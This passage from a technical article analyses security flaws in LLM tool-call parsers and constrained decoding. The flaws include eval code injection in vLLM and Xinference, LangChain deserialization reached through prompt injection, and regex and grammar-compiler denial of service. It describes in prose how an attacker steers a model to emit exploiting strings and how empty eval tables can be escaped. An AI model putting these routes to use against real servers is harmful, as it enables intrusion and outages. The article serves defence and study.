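From 54 characters on, each additional 16 characters multiplied the time by more than 20. If the time kept growing at the rate of the last step, a string of 118 characters would take about two hours and one of 134 characters about two days.

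The pattern runs on the model's output, so the attacker has to get the model to write the string. Getting a model to repeat a hundred characters is easy, as the Repeat-After-Me attack shows. OSV's *CVE-2025-48887* (2025) rates the flaw 6.5 out of 10, or medium severity. The rating assumes an attacker with an ordinary account and no help from another user, and counts only the loss of service. While the search runs, the request may also hold its share of the graphics processor's memory, making it unavailable to other requests.

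The flaw affected versions from 0.6.4 up to but not including 0.9.0, according to NVD's *CVE-2025-48887 Detail*. The fix changed the pattern so that matching time grows with the square of the string's length instead of exponentially. The advisory warns that the new pattern may still be a problem. If 100 characters took a tenth of a millisecond, quadratic growth would mean that 100,000 characters took 100 seconds.

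A more thorough fix is a search program that doesn't backtrack. It follows all possible matches at once as it reads the string, so its running time grows only in proportion to the string's length. In *chore(parsers): Mapping vllm parser tests to new PARSER_CASES.md taxonomy*, a comparison of test suites, zhongdaor-nv (2026) notes that Dynamo relies on this property of Rust's regular expressions, while vLLM has tests for what happens when a search exceeds its time limit. A time limit protects the server, but a search that hits it can miss a legitimate call.

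Streaming can bring quadratic growth back even with a fast search. vLLM gives its parsers the whole output so far along with each new piece. If an answer's *n* tokens arrive one at a time, a parser that searches the whole output each time reads 1 + 2 + … + *n* = *n*(*n* + 1)/2 tokens, or about 50 million for a 10,000-token answer. The GLM-4 parser avoids most of this work by searching only its buffer.

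### An error that stopped the server

In 2025, llama.cpp, a popular program for running models on one's own computer, had a simpler flaw. When a model's output resembled a tool call but was invalid, the parser raised an error that no code handled, which crashed the program, including its server version. Any sufficiently broken call could trigger the crash, so an attacker needed no special string, and a model could cause it by accident.

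Stankiewicz's *llama-chat : Do not throw when tool parsing fails* fixed this by catching the error and returning the model's text as an ordinary answer. vLLM's GLM-4 parser does the same when it fails on a complete answer. This keeps the server running, but an orchestrator that continues only while answers contain tool calls would treat the broken call as a final answer and end the task. The user might see raw markup, and the model would get no error message that could help it try again.

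### Repair or reject

Parsers need a rule for calls they can't fully read. NVIDIA's rules, published in November 2026 with a set of test cases, are to preserve valid data, keep the model's markup out of the visible answer, and not guess the intended call. Six months earlier, Dynamo had no common rule for malformed calls, and its list of test cases left recovery to each parser.

Suppose a model writes two calls to `write_file`, and the output reaches its length limit in the middle of the second. Under NVIDIA's rules, the parser should keep the first call and any text before it, but it should not run the second call or show its markup to the user. While the stream is still open, though, the parser can't distinguish a broken call from one that is still arriving.

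Many parsers use guesswork to recover incomplete calls. vllm-mlx's *qwen3 xml tool parser* adds missing closing tags to extract a call that was cut off. Hugging Face's *qwen3coder tool parser*, a file on the company's model-sharing site, uses patterns that let an unclosed call or argument run to the end of the text. Ambi's *Tool Parser*, part of an agent framework, cuts incomplete JSON back to its last closing brace and emits a format error if the result can't be parsed.

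Repair can turn an incomplete call into a harmful one. Here the user has asked the agent to revise a long report, and the output stops partway through:

```json
{"path": "report.txt", "overwrite": true, "text": "The first half of the rep
```

A parser that adds the missing quotation mark and brace produces a schema-valid call that replaces the whole report with its first half, and the tool reports success. If the model had put `overwrite` last, as in the earlier examples, the repaired call would have lacked a required argument and failed the schema check. Field order has no meaning in JSON, so nobody should depend on it for protection. A truncated path is just as dangerous in a tool that deletes folders, because the start of a path often names a folder that contains the intended one.

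An attacker may be able to influence where a call is cut off by making the model write more text before it, because the length limit is usually a fixed number of tokens.

The case for repair is reliability. A second attempt takes time and costs money, and if the length limit caused the failure, the model may hit it again. The orchestrator has to tell the model why the call failed so that the model can write the file in smaller parts. Discarding too much is also a bug. Overstreet (2026), in *context*, fixed a parser that lost almost everything in an unfinished block when the stream ended early. Only the last eight or so bytes survived, because the parser had held them back in case they were the start of a closing marker.

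Rejection can also be stricter than necessary. Ronacher describes how newer Claude models sometimes added invented fields to calls for an editing tool in Pi, a coding agent. The edits were usually correct, but Pi rejected the calls because they broke the schema, and had the model retry. Removing the unknown fields would have avoided the retry, but it would have meant assuming that they had no purpose. That assumption is safer for a meaningless extra label than for a field such as `dry_run`, which would be intended to prevent a change.

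Saving an incomplete call can also cause errors. The developer Jean Mertz found that an agent program kept incomplete calls in its conversation history. The calls had never run, so they had no results, and providers including Anthropic reject a conversation that contains a call without a result. One interrupted answer could therefore make the next request fail. Mertz's fix drops the incomplete call with a warning and keeps any partial text or reasoning.

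A parser can complete an unfinished call without guessing if every valid ending would give the same tool name and arguments. For example, if the model has written the final brace of the JSON object and only the closing marker is missing, nothing that follows can change the arguments. If the output stops inside `text`, countless endings are possible, and adding a quotation mark would be a guess. The rule could be looser for tools that only read data, since a search for half a phrase mostly wastes time, but even a search can send private text to an outside service.

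A response can be cut off after the model has written a complete call. For example, a model might write one call that deletes an old file and another that creates its replacement, and reach the length limit during the second. Dynamo has an option that sends each call to the orchestrator as soon as it is complete, so the file could be deleted before the second call was cut off. Kosec and colleagues introduced the option to save time. In the one response for which they give a full timeline, the call was complete after 800 milliseconds and the response ended after 814, so starting the tool early could have saved at most 14 milliseconds. The saving is larger when more text or further calls follow. An orchestrator could start harmless reads at once and hold calls that change something until the response has ended properly.

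## Turning text into typed values

Once the parser has found where an argument starts and ends, it has only a piece of text, but the tool needs a value of a particular type. JSON's notation mostly shows the type, but when an argument is written between tags, the converter has to look up the type in the schema. Modular's serving system therefore gives the parser each tool's schema before streaming begins. Coercion means changing a value from one type to another, such as turning the text `5` into the number 5.

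### Rules for each type

vLLM's first parser for Qwen3-Coder, a family of programming models from Alibaba, shows what this code involves. It checked the following cases in order and stopped at the first that applied.

| Case | What the parser did with the text |
|---|---|
| The text is `null`, in capitals or small letters | Turned it into `None`, Python's value for "nothing", whatever the declared type |
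| The schema doesn't list the argument, or lists it without a type | Kept it as a string |
| The type is a string, or a similar name such as `varchar` | Kept it as a string |
| The type is an integer | Read it as an integer, or kept the text if that failed |
| The type is a number | Read it as a floating-point number and turned whole results into integers, or kept the text if that failed |
| The type is Boolean | Turned `true` into true and everything else into false |
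| The type is an object | Tried to read it as JSON, then ran it as Python code |
| The type is anything else, including an array | Ran it as Python code |

Developers use type names that are not in JSON Schema, such as the database type `varchar`, and the parser tried to map these to JSON Schema types. But it treated `binary` as another name for Boolean, so if a developer declared a file's contents as `binary`, the tool would receive false instead of the file.

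Parsers also differ in how they handle text that doesn't match an argument's type. If the model writes `yes` for the boolean `overwrite`, the Qwen3-Coder parser produces false and logs a warning that never reaches the orchestrator. A newer vLLM parser, for the HY V3 models, passes on the text `yes`, which a schema check would then reject. False is the safe value for `overwrite`, but for an argument called `dry_run` it would mean making the change for real.

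Some schemas allow several types for one argument. The HY V3 parser tries Booleans first, then integers, other numbers, JSON and finally strings. If an argument can be an integer or a string, the product code `007` therefore becomes the number 7.

Sometimes the converter has no schema. *fix(parsing): vLLM-parity type ladder for XML tool-call arg coercion* (hallerite, 2026) proposed vLLM's rules for Renderers, a library whose parsed output is used in training. An automated reviewer pointed out that the library's parser for Nemotron 3 models never receives the schema. The old code tried to read every value as JSON, so `42` became a number, but under the new rules it would remain text. The old behavior is wrong for a postcode, which should stay text, and the new one is wrong for a quantity, so the parser can't choose the right type from the text alone.

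### CVE-2025-9141: code in an argument

The last two rows of the table contained a serious vulnerability. Python's `eval` function runs text as a Python expression. Given `[1, 2]`, it returns a list, which is what the parser's developers wanted, but if the text calls a function, `eval` runs that function on the model server with the server's permissions. Conversion comes before the schema check, the permission check and any request for the user's approval, so none of these could stop the code, which could run even if the tool never did.

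According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2014* (2026), the attack works only if the operator has turned on automatic tool calling and selected the `qwen3_coder` parser, and the argument's type is undefined or unrecognized. The attacker also needs an account on the server and has to get the model to write the code as an argument.

The flaw was broader than the third precondition suggests, because even a tool with an ordinary schema could expose the server. The vulnerable code treated a missing type as a string, which was safe. But it passed every array argument to `eval`, and `array` is a standard JSON Schema type. It did the same with any object argument that was not valid JSON, and with any argument whose type was a list such as `["string", "null"]`, a common way to make a string optional.

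The schema also arrives with each request, so a customer attacking a shared server could declare an array argument and ask the model to fill it with code. Someone attacking through a hostile web page would have to find an application that already offered a suitable tool.

Streaming gave no protection, because the parser still ran `eval` on the arguments. It sent every streamed value to the application as a string, but at the end of each call it converted the arguments again for its own records. This second conversion used `eval` too, and the parser ignored any error it raised.

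The flaw affected vLLM versions 0.10.0 and 0.10.1 and has a severity of 8.8 out of 10. Snyk's *Deserialization of Untrusted Data Affecting vllm package* (2025) credits Levi Gross with the discovery and dates the disclosure to 21 August 2025. Red Hat's *CVE-2025-9141* explains that the flaw was not rated critical because exploiting it requires a valid login. In version 0.10.1.1, which fixed the flaw, vLLM tries JSON for arrays as well as objects, then falls back on `ast.literal_eval`, a Python function that builds values from text without running it as code.

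### CVE-2026-61539: the whole output as code

A year later, researchers found a similar flaw in Xinference, another program for serving models. Its Llama 3 parser was designed for tool calls written as Python dictionaries, and it passed the model's entire output to `eval`. According to Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-61539* (2026), two files contained this mistake, and any chat request with a list of tools could reach it.

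The argument types made no difference here because the parser evaluated the output before processing individual arguments. An attack needed a server running Llama 3 through Transformers, one of the libraries that Xinference can use to run models. The model also had to output the attacker's expression and nothing else, because `eval` accepts only a complete expression and a sentence before the code would have caused a syntax error. The Repeat-After-Me attack also required the model to add no other text.

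Hatagale (2026) notes in *CVE-2026-61539* that Xinference requires no login by default. Anyone who could reach the server over the network could try the attack as often as they liked. The flaw scores the maximum of 10 partly for this reason and partly because it is rated as causing damage beyond Xinference itself, which the vLLM flaw is not.

Hatagale credits Guannan Wang, Zhanpeng Liu and Guancheng Li of Tencent's Xuanwu Lab, who used an automated engine called Atuin to find vulnerabilities. Version 2.7.0 replaced every use of `eval` in the tool parsers. GCVE's *mal-2026-3000* (2026) records that versions 2.6.0, 2.6.1 and 2.6.2 contained malicious code that stole passwords, keys and other secrets, so operators of version 2.5.0 or earlier should upgrade straight to 2.7.0.

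### Why empty variable tables don't help

Xinference called `eval` with two empty tables. Python looks up the names of variables and functions in these tables, so an expression that runs with empty ones might seem limited to harmless arithmetic. But if the table of global names has no entry for Python's built-in functions, `eval` adds one automatically. A harmless call demonstrates this:

```python
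eval('len("abc")', {}, {})    # 3
```

Python finds the function `len` even when both tables are empty. It finds the built-in import function the same way, and that function can load the module that runs operating-system commands.

A developer can block the built-in functions by supplying an empty entry for them, and the call above then fails. But an attacker's expression can avoid the built-in functions by starting from an ordinary value, such as an empty list, looking up its class and moving from there to other classes in the running program. Some of these can open files or start other programs. A developer who tries to block every such route is likely to miss one. Even plain arithmetic can freeze the server if the expression computes a large enough power.

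### Parsers that build values without running text

A JSON parser recognizes objects, arrays, strings, numbers, `true`, `false` and `null`. It has no rule for calling a function, so text that contains a function call is a syntax error.

Python's `ast.literal_eval` accepts Python notation. It first parses the text, without running it, into a tree in which lists, numbers and function calls are different kinds of node. It then builds values from the nodes that stand for plain data, and raises an error if it meets a function call or a variable. The Python-style parser in EasyDeL, a machine-learning library, is stricter and accepts only constants, lists, and dictionaries with constant keys.

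| Text | `eval` | `ast.literal_eval` | JSON parser |
|---|---|---|---|
| `[1, 2]` | A list | A list | A list |
| `{'a': True}` | A dictionary | A dictionary | Error |
| `{"a": true}` | Error | Error | An object |
| `len("abc")` | Runs the function and returns 3 | Error | Error |

The second row helps explain why developers chose `eval`. Models often write Python's `True` and single quotation marks where JSON requires `true` and double quotation marks, so a JSON-only parser would reject these calls. Trying JSON first and `ast.literal_eval` second accepts both notations without running the output as code.

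Literal-only parsing can still fail in other ways. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-1549* (2026) describes a flaw in LiteLLM, a gateway between applications and models, that let users without an account crash the server through its use of `ast.literal_eval`. Deeply nested brackets, for example, can exhaust the memory available for parsing. A converter should therefore limit the length and nesting of a value before parsing it.

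The repaired vLLM parser has a less serious problem. Suppose a tool expects an array and the model writes `{"a", "b"}`. This is invalid JSON but a valid Python set, so `ast.literal_eval` accepts it. An error then occurs when the parser converts the arguments to JSON, which has no sets. For a complete answer, vLLM handles this error by returning the whole output as ordinary text, so a single odd argument cancels every call in the answer, including the valid ones. The number `1e999` has the same effect in an argument of type `number`. It is too large for a floating-point number, so Python reads it as infinity, and the parser fails when converting infinity to an integer.

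### Why the mistake came back

Xinference's flaw became public on 21 August 2026, exactly one year after the date Snyk gives for vLLM's. Both projects used `eval` for the same convenience, though security guides had warned against running untrusted text as code long before language models existed. The mistake is also easy to spot because a text search for `eval` finds every use.

Wiz's *CVE-2025-9141* reports that a Google review bot flagged the parser's `eval` call as a critical vulnerability, but vLLM's developers still added the parser in July 2025. The page is AI-generated, so its account should be treated with some caution. If it is true, a rule that blocks new code containing `eval` would have helped more than another tool for finding it.

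Parsers also spread by copying. Hugging Face hosts an undated copy of the Qwen3-Coder parser that still contains the `eval` call, and an operator who loads that file can bring the flaw back to a patched server. Copying can also spread the safer design. A class in NVIDIA's *core.tokenizers.text.parsers.qwen3_coder_tool_parser* has the same method names as vLLM's repaired parser.

Snyk files the vLLM flaw under CWE-502, unsafe deserialization, while the record for the Xinference flaw uses CWE-95, code injection through `eval`. A developer who searched past vulnerabilities for only one of these labels would miss the other flaw.

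### Saved data that comes back as an object

Deserialization means rebuilding a program's objects from saved text. It is risky when the text can determine which kind of object the program builds, even if the program never calls `eval`.

LangChain, a framework for building agents, had such a flaw. Its functions `dumps()` and `dumpd()` prepare objects for saving and mark LangChain's own objects with the key `lc`. OSV's *CVE-2025-68664* (2025) explains that these functions did not escape the key in ordinary dictionaries. If an attacker's data contained the key in the right structure, LangChain saved the data unchanged and later read it back as one of its own objects. Like the markers around tool calls, the `lc` key is a signal in the same channel as the data.

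PT Security's *Langchain · Langchain · CVE-2025-68664* notes that prompt injection can exploit the flaw through a model's response. The attacker gets the model to include the structure in its answer, then waits for the application to save and reload the answer. The attack can work even if the code that parsed the original answer worked correctly.

Loading the false object could reveal secrets such as the passwords and keys that servers often keep in environment variables. Sources differ on whether an attacker could also run code. Red Hat's *CVE-2025-68664* states that remote attackers could run arbitrary code, but OSV's score of 9.3 is based on a serious loss of secrets, only limited changes to data and no loss of service. Full code execution would normally rate higher for both changes to data and loss of service. LangChain fixed the flaw in versions 0.3.81 and 1.2.5, and OSV published its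 entry on 23 December 2025.

### When "false" counts as true

Many conversion errors produce no crash and no message. In Python, every non-empty string counts as true, including this one:

```python
bool("false")    # True
```

The first Qwen3-Coder parser could trigger this error in ordinary use. When it streamed a call to `write_file`, it sent every value as a string, so `false` arrived as `"false"`. If the orchestrator skipped the schema check and the tool contained the line `if overwrite:`, the tool would replace the file the user had asked it to protect. If the answer had been parsed whole instead of streamed, the same parser would have sent a real Boolean, and the tool would have left the file alone.

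A strict schema check stops this call because `"false"` is a string and the schema requires a Boolean. A tool that has to accept text should compare it with the exact words `true` and `false` and reject anything else.

### Large numbers and repeated names

Most programs store floating-point numbers with 53 binary digits of precision. This is enough for every whole number up to 2⁵³, or 9,007,199,254,740,992. Just above that limit only even numbers fit, so an odd number changes to a neighbor:

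```python
int("9007199254740993")           # 9007199254740993
int(float("9007199254740993"))    # 9007199254740992
```

Both versions of vLLM's Qwen3-Coder parser use the second method for arguments of type `number`, but not `integer`. The HY V3 parser avoids the error by reading text as an integer unless it contains a decimal point or an exponent. But JavaScript's standard JSON parser reads all numbers as floating-point, so an orchestrator written in JavaScript can still change a number that the serving software converted correctly.

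The rounding hardly matters for a measurement, but it can make an identifier refer to a different item. A tool asked to delete message 9007199254740993 would delete message 9007199254740992 instead. Both numbers satisfy the schema, so the schema check can't detect the change. Sending identifiers as strings avoids the problem.

Repeated names are another way for two programs to read the same call differently:

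```json
{"path": "notes/today.txt", "text": "", "overwrite": false, "overwrite": true}
```

The JSON standard advises against repeated names in an object but doesn't forbid them. The standard parsers in Python and JavaScript keep the last value without reporting an error, while some other parsers keep the first. If the program that asks for the user's approval keeps the first value and the tool keeps the last, the user can approve a harmless call while the tool runs one that empties a file.

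An attacker might add the second copy by closing the `text` argument early, as described for the GLM-4 parser. Like the GLM-4 parser, the HY V3 parser keeps the first copy in a streamed answer but the last in a complete one. The first Qwen3-Coder parser passed on both copies when streaming, so which one was used depended on the next program.

The safest response to a repeated name in a call's JSON is to reject the call. Python's JSON parser can pass every name and value to a function that checks for repeats. If the call isn't rejected, the program that checks it should write new JSON from the values it checked and send only that to the tool, so that the tool can't use a different value for the same name.

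### The word "null"

Both versions of vLLM's Qwen3-Coder parser convert the text `null` to `None` before checking the declared type. If a user asks an agent to save a file containing only the word "null", `write_file` receives `None` instead of the text. A schema check would reject the call, but retrying would also fail because the notation gives the model no other way to write the word.

hallerite's proposal for Renderers originally kept `null` as text in string arguments. A later change dropped this exception. The stated reason was that programs further along follow vLLM's interpretation, and agreement with them matters more. For training this is a reasonable choice, since a model should learn from the same values that its tools will receive. It also turns a questionable rule in one popular parser into a convention.

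Python treats `None` as false in a condition, which can make null Boolean arguments dangerous. For example, a null `dry_run` lets a change go ahead, although a null `overwrite` leaves existing files alone. In a tool that deletes all records matching a filter, a null filter might match every record. Tools should reject null unless their schema explicitly allows it.

### Strict and lenient checking

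Developers often leave type checks to a validation library, and these libraries have different defaults. Pydantic, a popular Python library, is lenient by default. For a Boolean, it converts strings such as `"false"`, `"no"` and `"off"` to false and rejects unrecognized strings. If the developer turns on strict mode, it accepts only a real Boolean.

Zod, a TypeScript library, and Ajv, which checks data against JSON Schema in JavaScript, both leave types alone by default, but turning on coercion can produce unexpected booleans. Zod's coercion follows JavaScript's rule that any non-empty string is true, so `"false"` becomes true. Zod 4 has a separate function that reads such words correctly. Ajv's coercion converts `"false"` correctly, but it also turns null into false.

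Lenient checking avoids another round with the model when the intended value is obvious, as when the model writes `"5"` for a number. The risk grows when several programs each apply their own lenient rules, because the permission check and the tool may convert the same output to different values.

The converter is the best place to turn text into typed values because it has access to both the notation and the schema. It can accept the letters `false` between tags as a Boolean and treat `"false"` in JSON as the model's mistake. Every later program can then check the typed values strictly. Renderers also distinguishes a successful conversion from a guess. If a Boolean argument contains `yes`, it returns false as a guess, with a status that marks the value as invalid, so the calling code can reject the call.

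## Forcing valid output with a grammar

Constrained decoding is meant to prevent the model from generating malformed calls, which cause problems in both the parser and the type conversion.

### From a schema to a list of allowed tokens

The engine, the software that runs the model, first compiles the schema into a grammar. For `write_file`, the grammar specifies the three fields, the punctuation between them and the form of each value. While the model writes, a matcher tracks the current position in the grammar, for example inside the string for `path` or just before the value of `overwrite`. For nested data, it also keeps a stack of open objects and arrays.

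Let *L* be the set of complete outputs that fit the grammar, and *s* the text so far. A token *t* is allowed if adding it to *s* gives a text that could still grow into a member of *L*. The model assigns each token a probability *p*(*t*). The engine sets the probability of every forbidden token to zero and renormalizes, which means dividing the others by their total so that they add up to 1 again:

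```
q(t) = p(t) / (sum of p(u) over all allowed tokens u)    if t is allowed
q(t) = 0                                                 otherwise
```

The token that ends the output is allowed only when *s* is in *L*. After each step, the text can therefore still be completed into a valid output, and the model can stop only when the text is valid.

A token may cover several characters, such as `false}`, which finishes both the value and the object. The matcher has to check each token as a whole, and the gpt-oss vocabulary has more than 200,000 tokens. The grammar can also cover the markers around a tool call. NVIDIA's *Structural Tag (Guided Decoding for Tool Calls)* describes how Dynamo does this with XGrammar, an open-source library for compiling and matching grammars.

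### One step for `overwrite`

Suppose the model has written the first two arguments and then `"overwrite": `, and that only four tokens are at all likely to come next:

| Next token | Model's probability | Allowed? | Probability after masking |
|---|---|---|---|
| `"`, which opens a string such as `"no"` | 0.40 | No | 0 |
| `false` | 0.30 | Yes | 0.75 |
| `null` | 0.20 | No | 0 |
| `true` | 0.10 | Yes | 0.25 |

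The probabilities of the allowed tokens add up to 0.40, so `false` gets 0.30 / 0.40 = 0.75. The grammar ensures that the value is always a Boolean. Without it, the model would most often have started a string, and the call would have failed the schema check.

The chance of `true`, which replaces the user's file, has risen from 10% to 25%. If every string would have been `"no"`, the total probability was 70% for "no" and 10% for "yes", so `true` should have had only a 12.5% chance. Renormalization doesn't account for what the model would have generated after a blocked token. An engine that always picks the most likely token would choose `false` here, but it can make the same error when the probabilities are closer.

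The distortion is smaller if the model already puts little probability on forbidden tokens. This is a good reason to also describe the format in the prompt, as vLLM recommends. According to Anthropic's *Structured outputs*, the company adds such a description automatically when a developer asks for an answer in a JSON format.

### What the guarantee covers

If the output is complete, it fits the part of the schema that the engine supports. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* guide uses the example of a booking tool that needs a number of passengers. Without strict mode, the model might write `"two"` or `"2"`. With it, the value is the number `2`, which would still be wrong for a family of three. The guide says there is "No need to validate and retry tool calls", but at most this applies to the types of the values, not to whether they are correct or safe.

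The output may also be incomplete, because a string can be any length and the model may reach its token limit inside `text`. The orchestrator then has the usual problem of a truncated call. Field order helps a little. OpenAI's *Structured outputs* guide states that the output follows the order of the keys in the schema, and Anthropic does the same after moving required fields to the front. `overwrite` comes last under either rule, so a careless repair of a call cut off inside `text` would lack that field and fail the schema check.

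Refusals are another exception. When a Claude model refuses a strict request for safety reasons, the refusal takes precedence over the schema, but the HTTP status is still 200 (success), so the orchestrator has to check the stated reason for stopping as well as the status.

Anthropic's third exception is easier to miss because it produces no error. When a schema lists the allowed values of a string, the model may return one with different capitalization. If a tool's schema allowed only the folders `Meeting notes` and `Drafts`, the model could return `Meeting Notes`, which is a different folder on most Linux systems. Anthropic advises developers to ignore case when comparing these values. The tool should then use the spelling from its own list rather than the model's.

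A grammar can't establish that a tool call is authorized, and it can prevent the model from declining to make one. vLLM's `required` setting forces the model to produce at least one tool call. The engine blocks an answer such as "I can't do that" because it doesn't fit the grammar, so the model can avoid harm only through its choice of tool and arguments. Strict mode alone doesn't necessarily have this effect. *Strict tool calling* describes the strict mode of mistral.rs, another open-source engine, which constrains the arguments only if the model decides to make a call.

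A grammar also does not stop copied text in the XML-like notation from closing its argument early and supplying its own `overwrite`, because the result is valid under the grammar. If the grammar allows each field only once, it even blocks the `overwrite` that the model would have written afterwards.

### Strict modes and unsupported schemas

No major provider supports all of JSON Schema, and they differ in what they leave out:

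| Part of the schema | Anthropic | OpenAI |
|---|---|---|
| Minimum or maximum for a number | Error | Enforced |
| Pattern for a string | Enforced, except for features such as lookahead | Enforced |
| A schema that refers to itself | Error | Accepted |
| Optional fields | Up to 24 per request | None, but a field may allow null |

OpenAI's fine-tuned models, which customers have trained further, support neither number limits nor patterns.

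For `write_file`, a pattern can do much of the work of a path check:

```json
"path": {
  "type": "string",
  "pattern": "^[A-Za-z0-9_-]+(\\.[A-Za-z0-9]+)?(/[A-Za-z0-9_-]+(\\.[A-Za-z0-9]+)?)*$"
}
```

This pattern accepts the same paths as the earlier grammar for `write_file` and, like that grammar, can't detect symbolic links. It needs none of the features that Anthropic excludes. A developer who tried to express the rule as "anything without two dots in a row" would probably use lookahead, which checks what follows without consuming it. Anthropic rejects lookahead, and according to NVIDIA's *Structural Tag*, some versions of XGrammar can reject it too unless the developer sets `strict` to false for the tool.

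When a service returns an error, the developer at least knows that the rule is not in force. AWS's *Structured output* describes the same policy for Amazon Bedrock, which returns an error before compiling anything. According to a comparison by dottxt, a vendor of structured-output software, Google's Gemini silently ignores the properties it doesn't support. If Gemini ignored a path pattern, the developer would believe the model could write only safe paths when it could write any path.

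Client libraries can weaken a schema as well. Most of Anthropic's helpers remove unsupported constraints before sending the schema and add them to the field's description, where they are only advice to the model. Some helpers then check the answer against the original schema, but with the others the orchestrator has to do this check.

In vLLM, a client that requests strict mode may not get it. In automatic mode, strict mode also depends on whether the selected parser supports it and whether the operator has disabled it for the whole server. Checking every call against the full schema is safest, even when the engine should already have enforced it.

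### A valid call with a character missing

In *Same Error, Different Recovery*, Woo, Conde and Reviriego (2026) studied how the presentation of an error message affects what a model does next. They ran the same tasks on llama.cpp, vLLM, SGLang and GeulPU, an engine that Woo wrote. The differences between engines in handling tool calls were larger than the effect under study.

In a pilot with Llama 3.1 8B, llama.cpp returned a server error for 34 of 85 requests (40%) because it could not parse the model's tool calls. Woo and colleagues don't explain what was wrong with the calls or report a fix. In the main experiment, llama.cpp ended 137 runs with errors, all with Llama 3.1 8B. vLLM ended 134 runs with errors and SGLang ended 120, but they did so because they rejected conversations in which the model had made several calls in one turn.

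A second failure shows a grammar's limits more directly. Woo and colleagues had the coding agent Qwen Code work on six small repositories, using Qwen3-32B among other models. They named the working folders after the engine, so the folder names for GeulPU contained Korean characters, which the model had to copy into file paths. At one rare character, the most likely next token was the special token that opens a new message. Its probability in GeulPU was 28%, compared with 7% for the correct character.

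GeulPU had no rule against that token, so the call broke off and the agent treated the fragment as the model's final answer. Calls broke off this way in 15 of 36 runs with Qwen3-32B. llama.cpp constrains tool calls with a grammar. On the same request, the special token had a probability of 21% in llama.cpp and the correct character had 14%. The call stayed well formed, but the path was missing that character.

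A path with one character missing is harder to catch than a malformed call because it passes the schema check. It may name a folder that doesn't exist or, worse, a different one that does. Woo and colleagues don't say which token llama.cpp chose in place of the special one. If the correct character ranked second, blocking the special token should have let llama.cpp choose it, so perhaps another token ranked between them.

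The fix is in GeulPU 0.15.0, not in llama.cpp. While a Qwen-style call is open, GeulPU blocks all special tokens except the one that closes the call and those that end the output. With this change, the request that had failed produced the complete, correct path. In six further runs with random sampling, the new version lost no calls and the old one lost three. This was a small test on one request, but the fix adds little overhead and leaves the output unchanged when no special token appears inside a call.

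In the same study, the prompt template for Qwen2.5-7B showed its example call in doubled braces, and the model copied them. GeulPU failed to recognize a single call in 1,734 replies until its developers changed the parser. A JSON grammar would probably have helped here, because it would have blocked the second brace.

### Schemas that crash the compiler

The grammar compiler is itself a parser, and on a shared server customers supply its input. An orchestrator may also forward schemas from a remote MCP server, so the operator of that MCP server can send input to the compiler without an account on the model server.

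XGrammar has had three flaws of this kind. In one, CVE-2026-25048, a grammar with 30,000 nested parentheses crashed the program (GCVE's *GHSA-7RGV-GQHR-FXG3*, 2026). The record classes the flaw as uncontrolled recursion. Parsers commonly handle nested parentheses with a function that calls itself at each opening one, and every unfinished call uses part of the call stack, a limited block of memory. OSV's *CVE-2026-25048* (2026) rates the flaw's severity 8.7 out of 10 and gives 0.1.32 as the first safe version. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-25048* lists an update for the company's commercial inference server, dated 20 days after the disclosure.

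CVE-2025-58446 made the compiler slow instead of crashing it. According to OSV's *CVE-2025-58446* (2025), version 0.1.23 introduced an optimizer that took a very long time to process grammars of more than 100,000 characters. A client could produce a grammar that long by listing a huge number of allowed values for a single argument. The next version fixed this.

The third flaw was in the cache where XGrammar keeps compiled grammars for reuse. According to GitLab's *Advisories for Pypi/Xgrammar package* (2025), the cache had no size limit, so a client could fill the server's memory by sending many small requests, each with a different schema. No single request looks suspicious, and a fuzzer that restarts the program for every input would never find the problem. An expiry time alone would not solve it, because an attacker can add entries faster than they expire.

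llama.cpp had a related flaw, CVE-2026-2069, in the function that works out which positions in a grammar can come next. If a grammar repeats an item that can be empty, and repeats the whole thing again, the function can match nothing, return to where it started and try again without end. VulDB's *llama.cpp commit 55abc39 Stack-based Buffer Overflow* describes how it calls itself until the stack runs out. The release notes for *ggml-org/llama.cpp b8467* describe a fix for an overflow in the same function, which records the positions it has already visited and stops when one comes up again.

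OSV's *CVE-2026-2069* (2026) rates this flaw only 3.3, and Red Hat's *CVE-2026-2069 llama.cpp* (2026) describes the attack as local. But the test case in the release notes sends the grammar to llama.cpp's server in an ordinary web request, so the rating is too low for servers that strangers can reach.

Translating a schema into a grammar is a separate step with its own flaws. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-17501* and Debian's *CVE-2026-52130* record uncontrolled recursion in the llama.cpp file that performs this translation. According to Red Hat's entry, an attacker can trigger the flaw remotely, and the fix is awaiting acceptance.

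Limits on schemas prevent much of this, but they also reject some legitimate schemas. Anthropic allows 20 strict tools per request and stops compiling after 180 seconds. Each optional field can roughly double part of the grammar, so even a modest schema can take a lot of computation to compile. *UPSTREAM PR #21139*, loci-dev's proposal to let operators change llama.cpp's fixed limit of 2,000 repetitions, reports that the limit blocked legitimate tools with many optional arguments.

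### Valid output that causes trouble

The client's schema or grammar triggers all of these compiler flaws, so the attacker doesn't have to influence the model, and the same request works every time. The author of a web page can't exploit them, because a page that an agent reads affects only what the model writes.

Model output reaches the matcher instead, one token at a time. The engine blocks forbidden tokens, so an attacker who steers the model can only use text that fits the grammar. Some valid text can still cause problems, because JSON allows any amount of space between its parts. OpenAI warns that in its older JSON mode, which guarantees valid JSON but no particular schema, a model without clear instructions may produce spaces until it reaches the token limit. XGrammar's *Tool Calling and Reasoning* notes that such output can overload the matcher, and describes a setting that limits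 the number of consecutive spaces.

Deep nesting can get through in the same way. If a schema refers to itself, its grammar may let the model keep opening brackets until it runs out of tokens. The converter therefore still needs its nesting limit, even though every call it receives is valid.

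## Fuzzing the converter

A converter is easy to fuzz because it doesn't need a model. It is a function that takes a string and a list of tools and returns visible text and tool calls. A fuzzer can run it thousands of times a second on outputs that a model would almost never write by itself.

### The algorithm

```
corpus = recorded model outputs, each with its list of tools
repeat until the time runs out:
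    pick an output and its tools from the corpus
    change the output, the tools or both
    run the converter on them, within time and memory limits
    if a property fails:
        shrink the input and save it as a regression test
    else if the run reached new code:
        add the input to the corpus
```

The test harness should call the parser directly, in both complete-answer and streaming modes. It needs a new parser object for every run, because a streaming parser keeps a buffer, and data left over from one input could change the result for the next. LLVM recommends narrow targets, one for each data format, so a server with 23 parsers needs 23 targets.

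Recorded outputs make good seeds because they contain the odd spacing, reasoning and mixed text that real models produce. Some projects already store them. For example, *fix* (elyasmnvidian, 2025) added recorded streams from vLLM and SGLang, another serving program, to a set of parser tests and paired each stream with its expected result. A fuzzer could start from the same files and ignore the expected results.

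The fuzzer then changes the seeds at several levels:

| Level | Example for `write_file` | Code under test |
|---|---|---|
| Bytes | Delete half of a two-byte character such as `é` | Text decoding |
| Tokens | Replace a special token with ordinary tokens that spell the same marker | Marker recognition |
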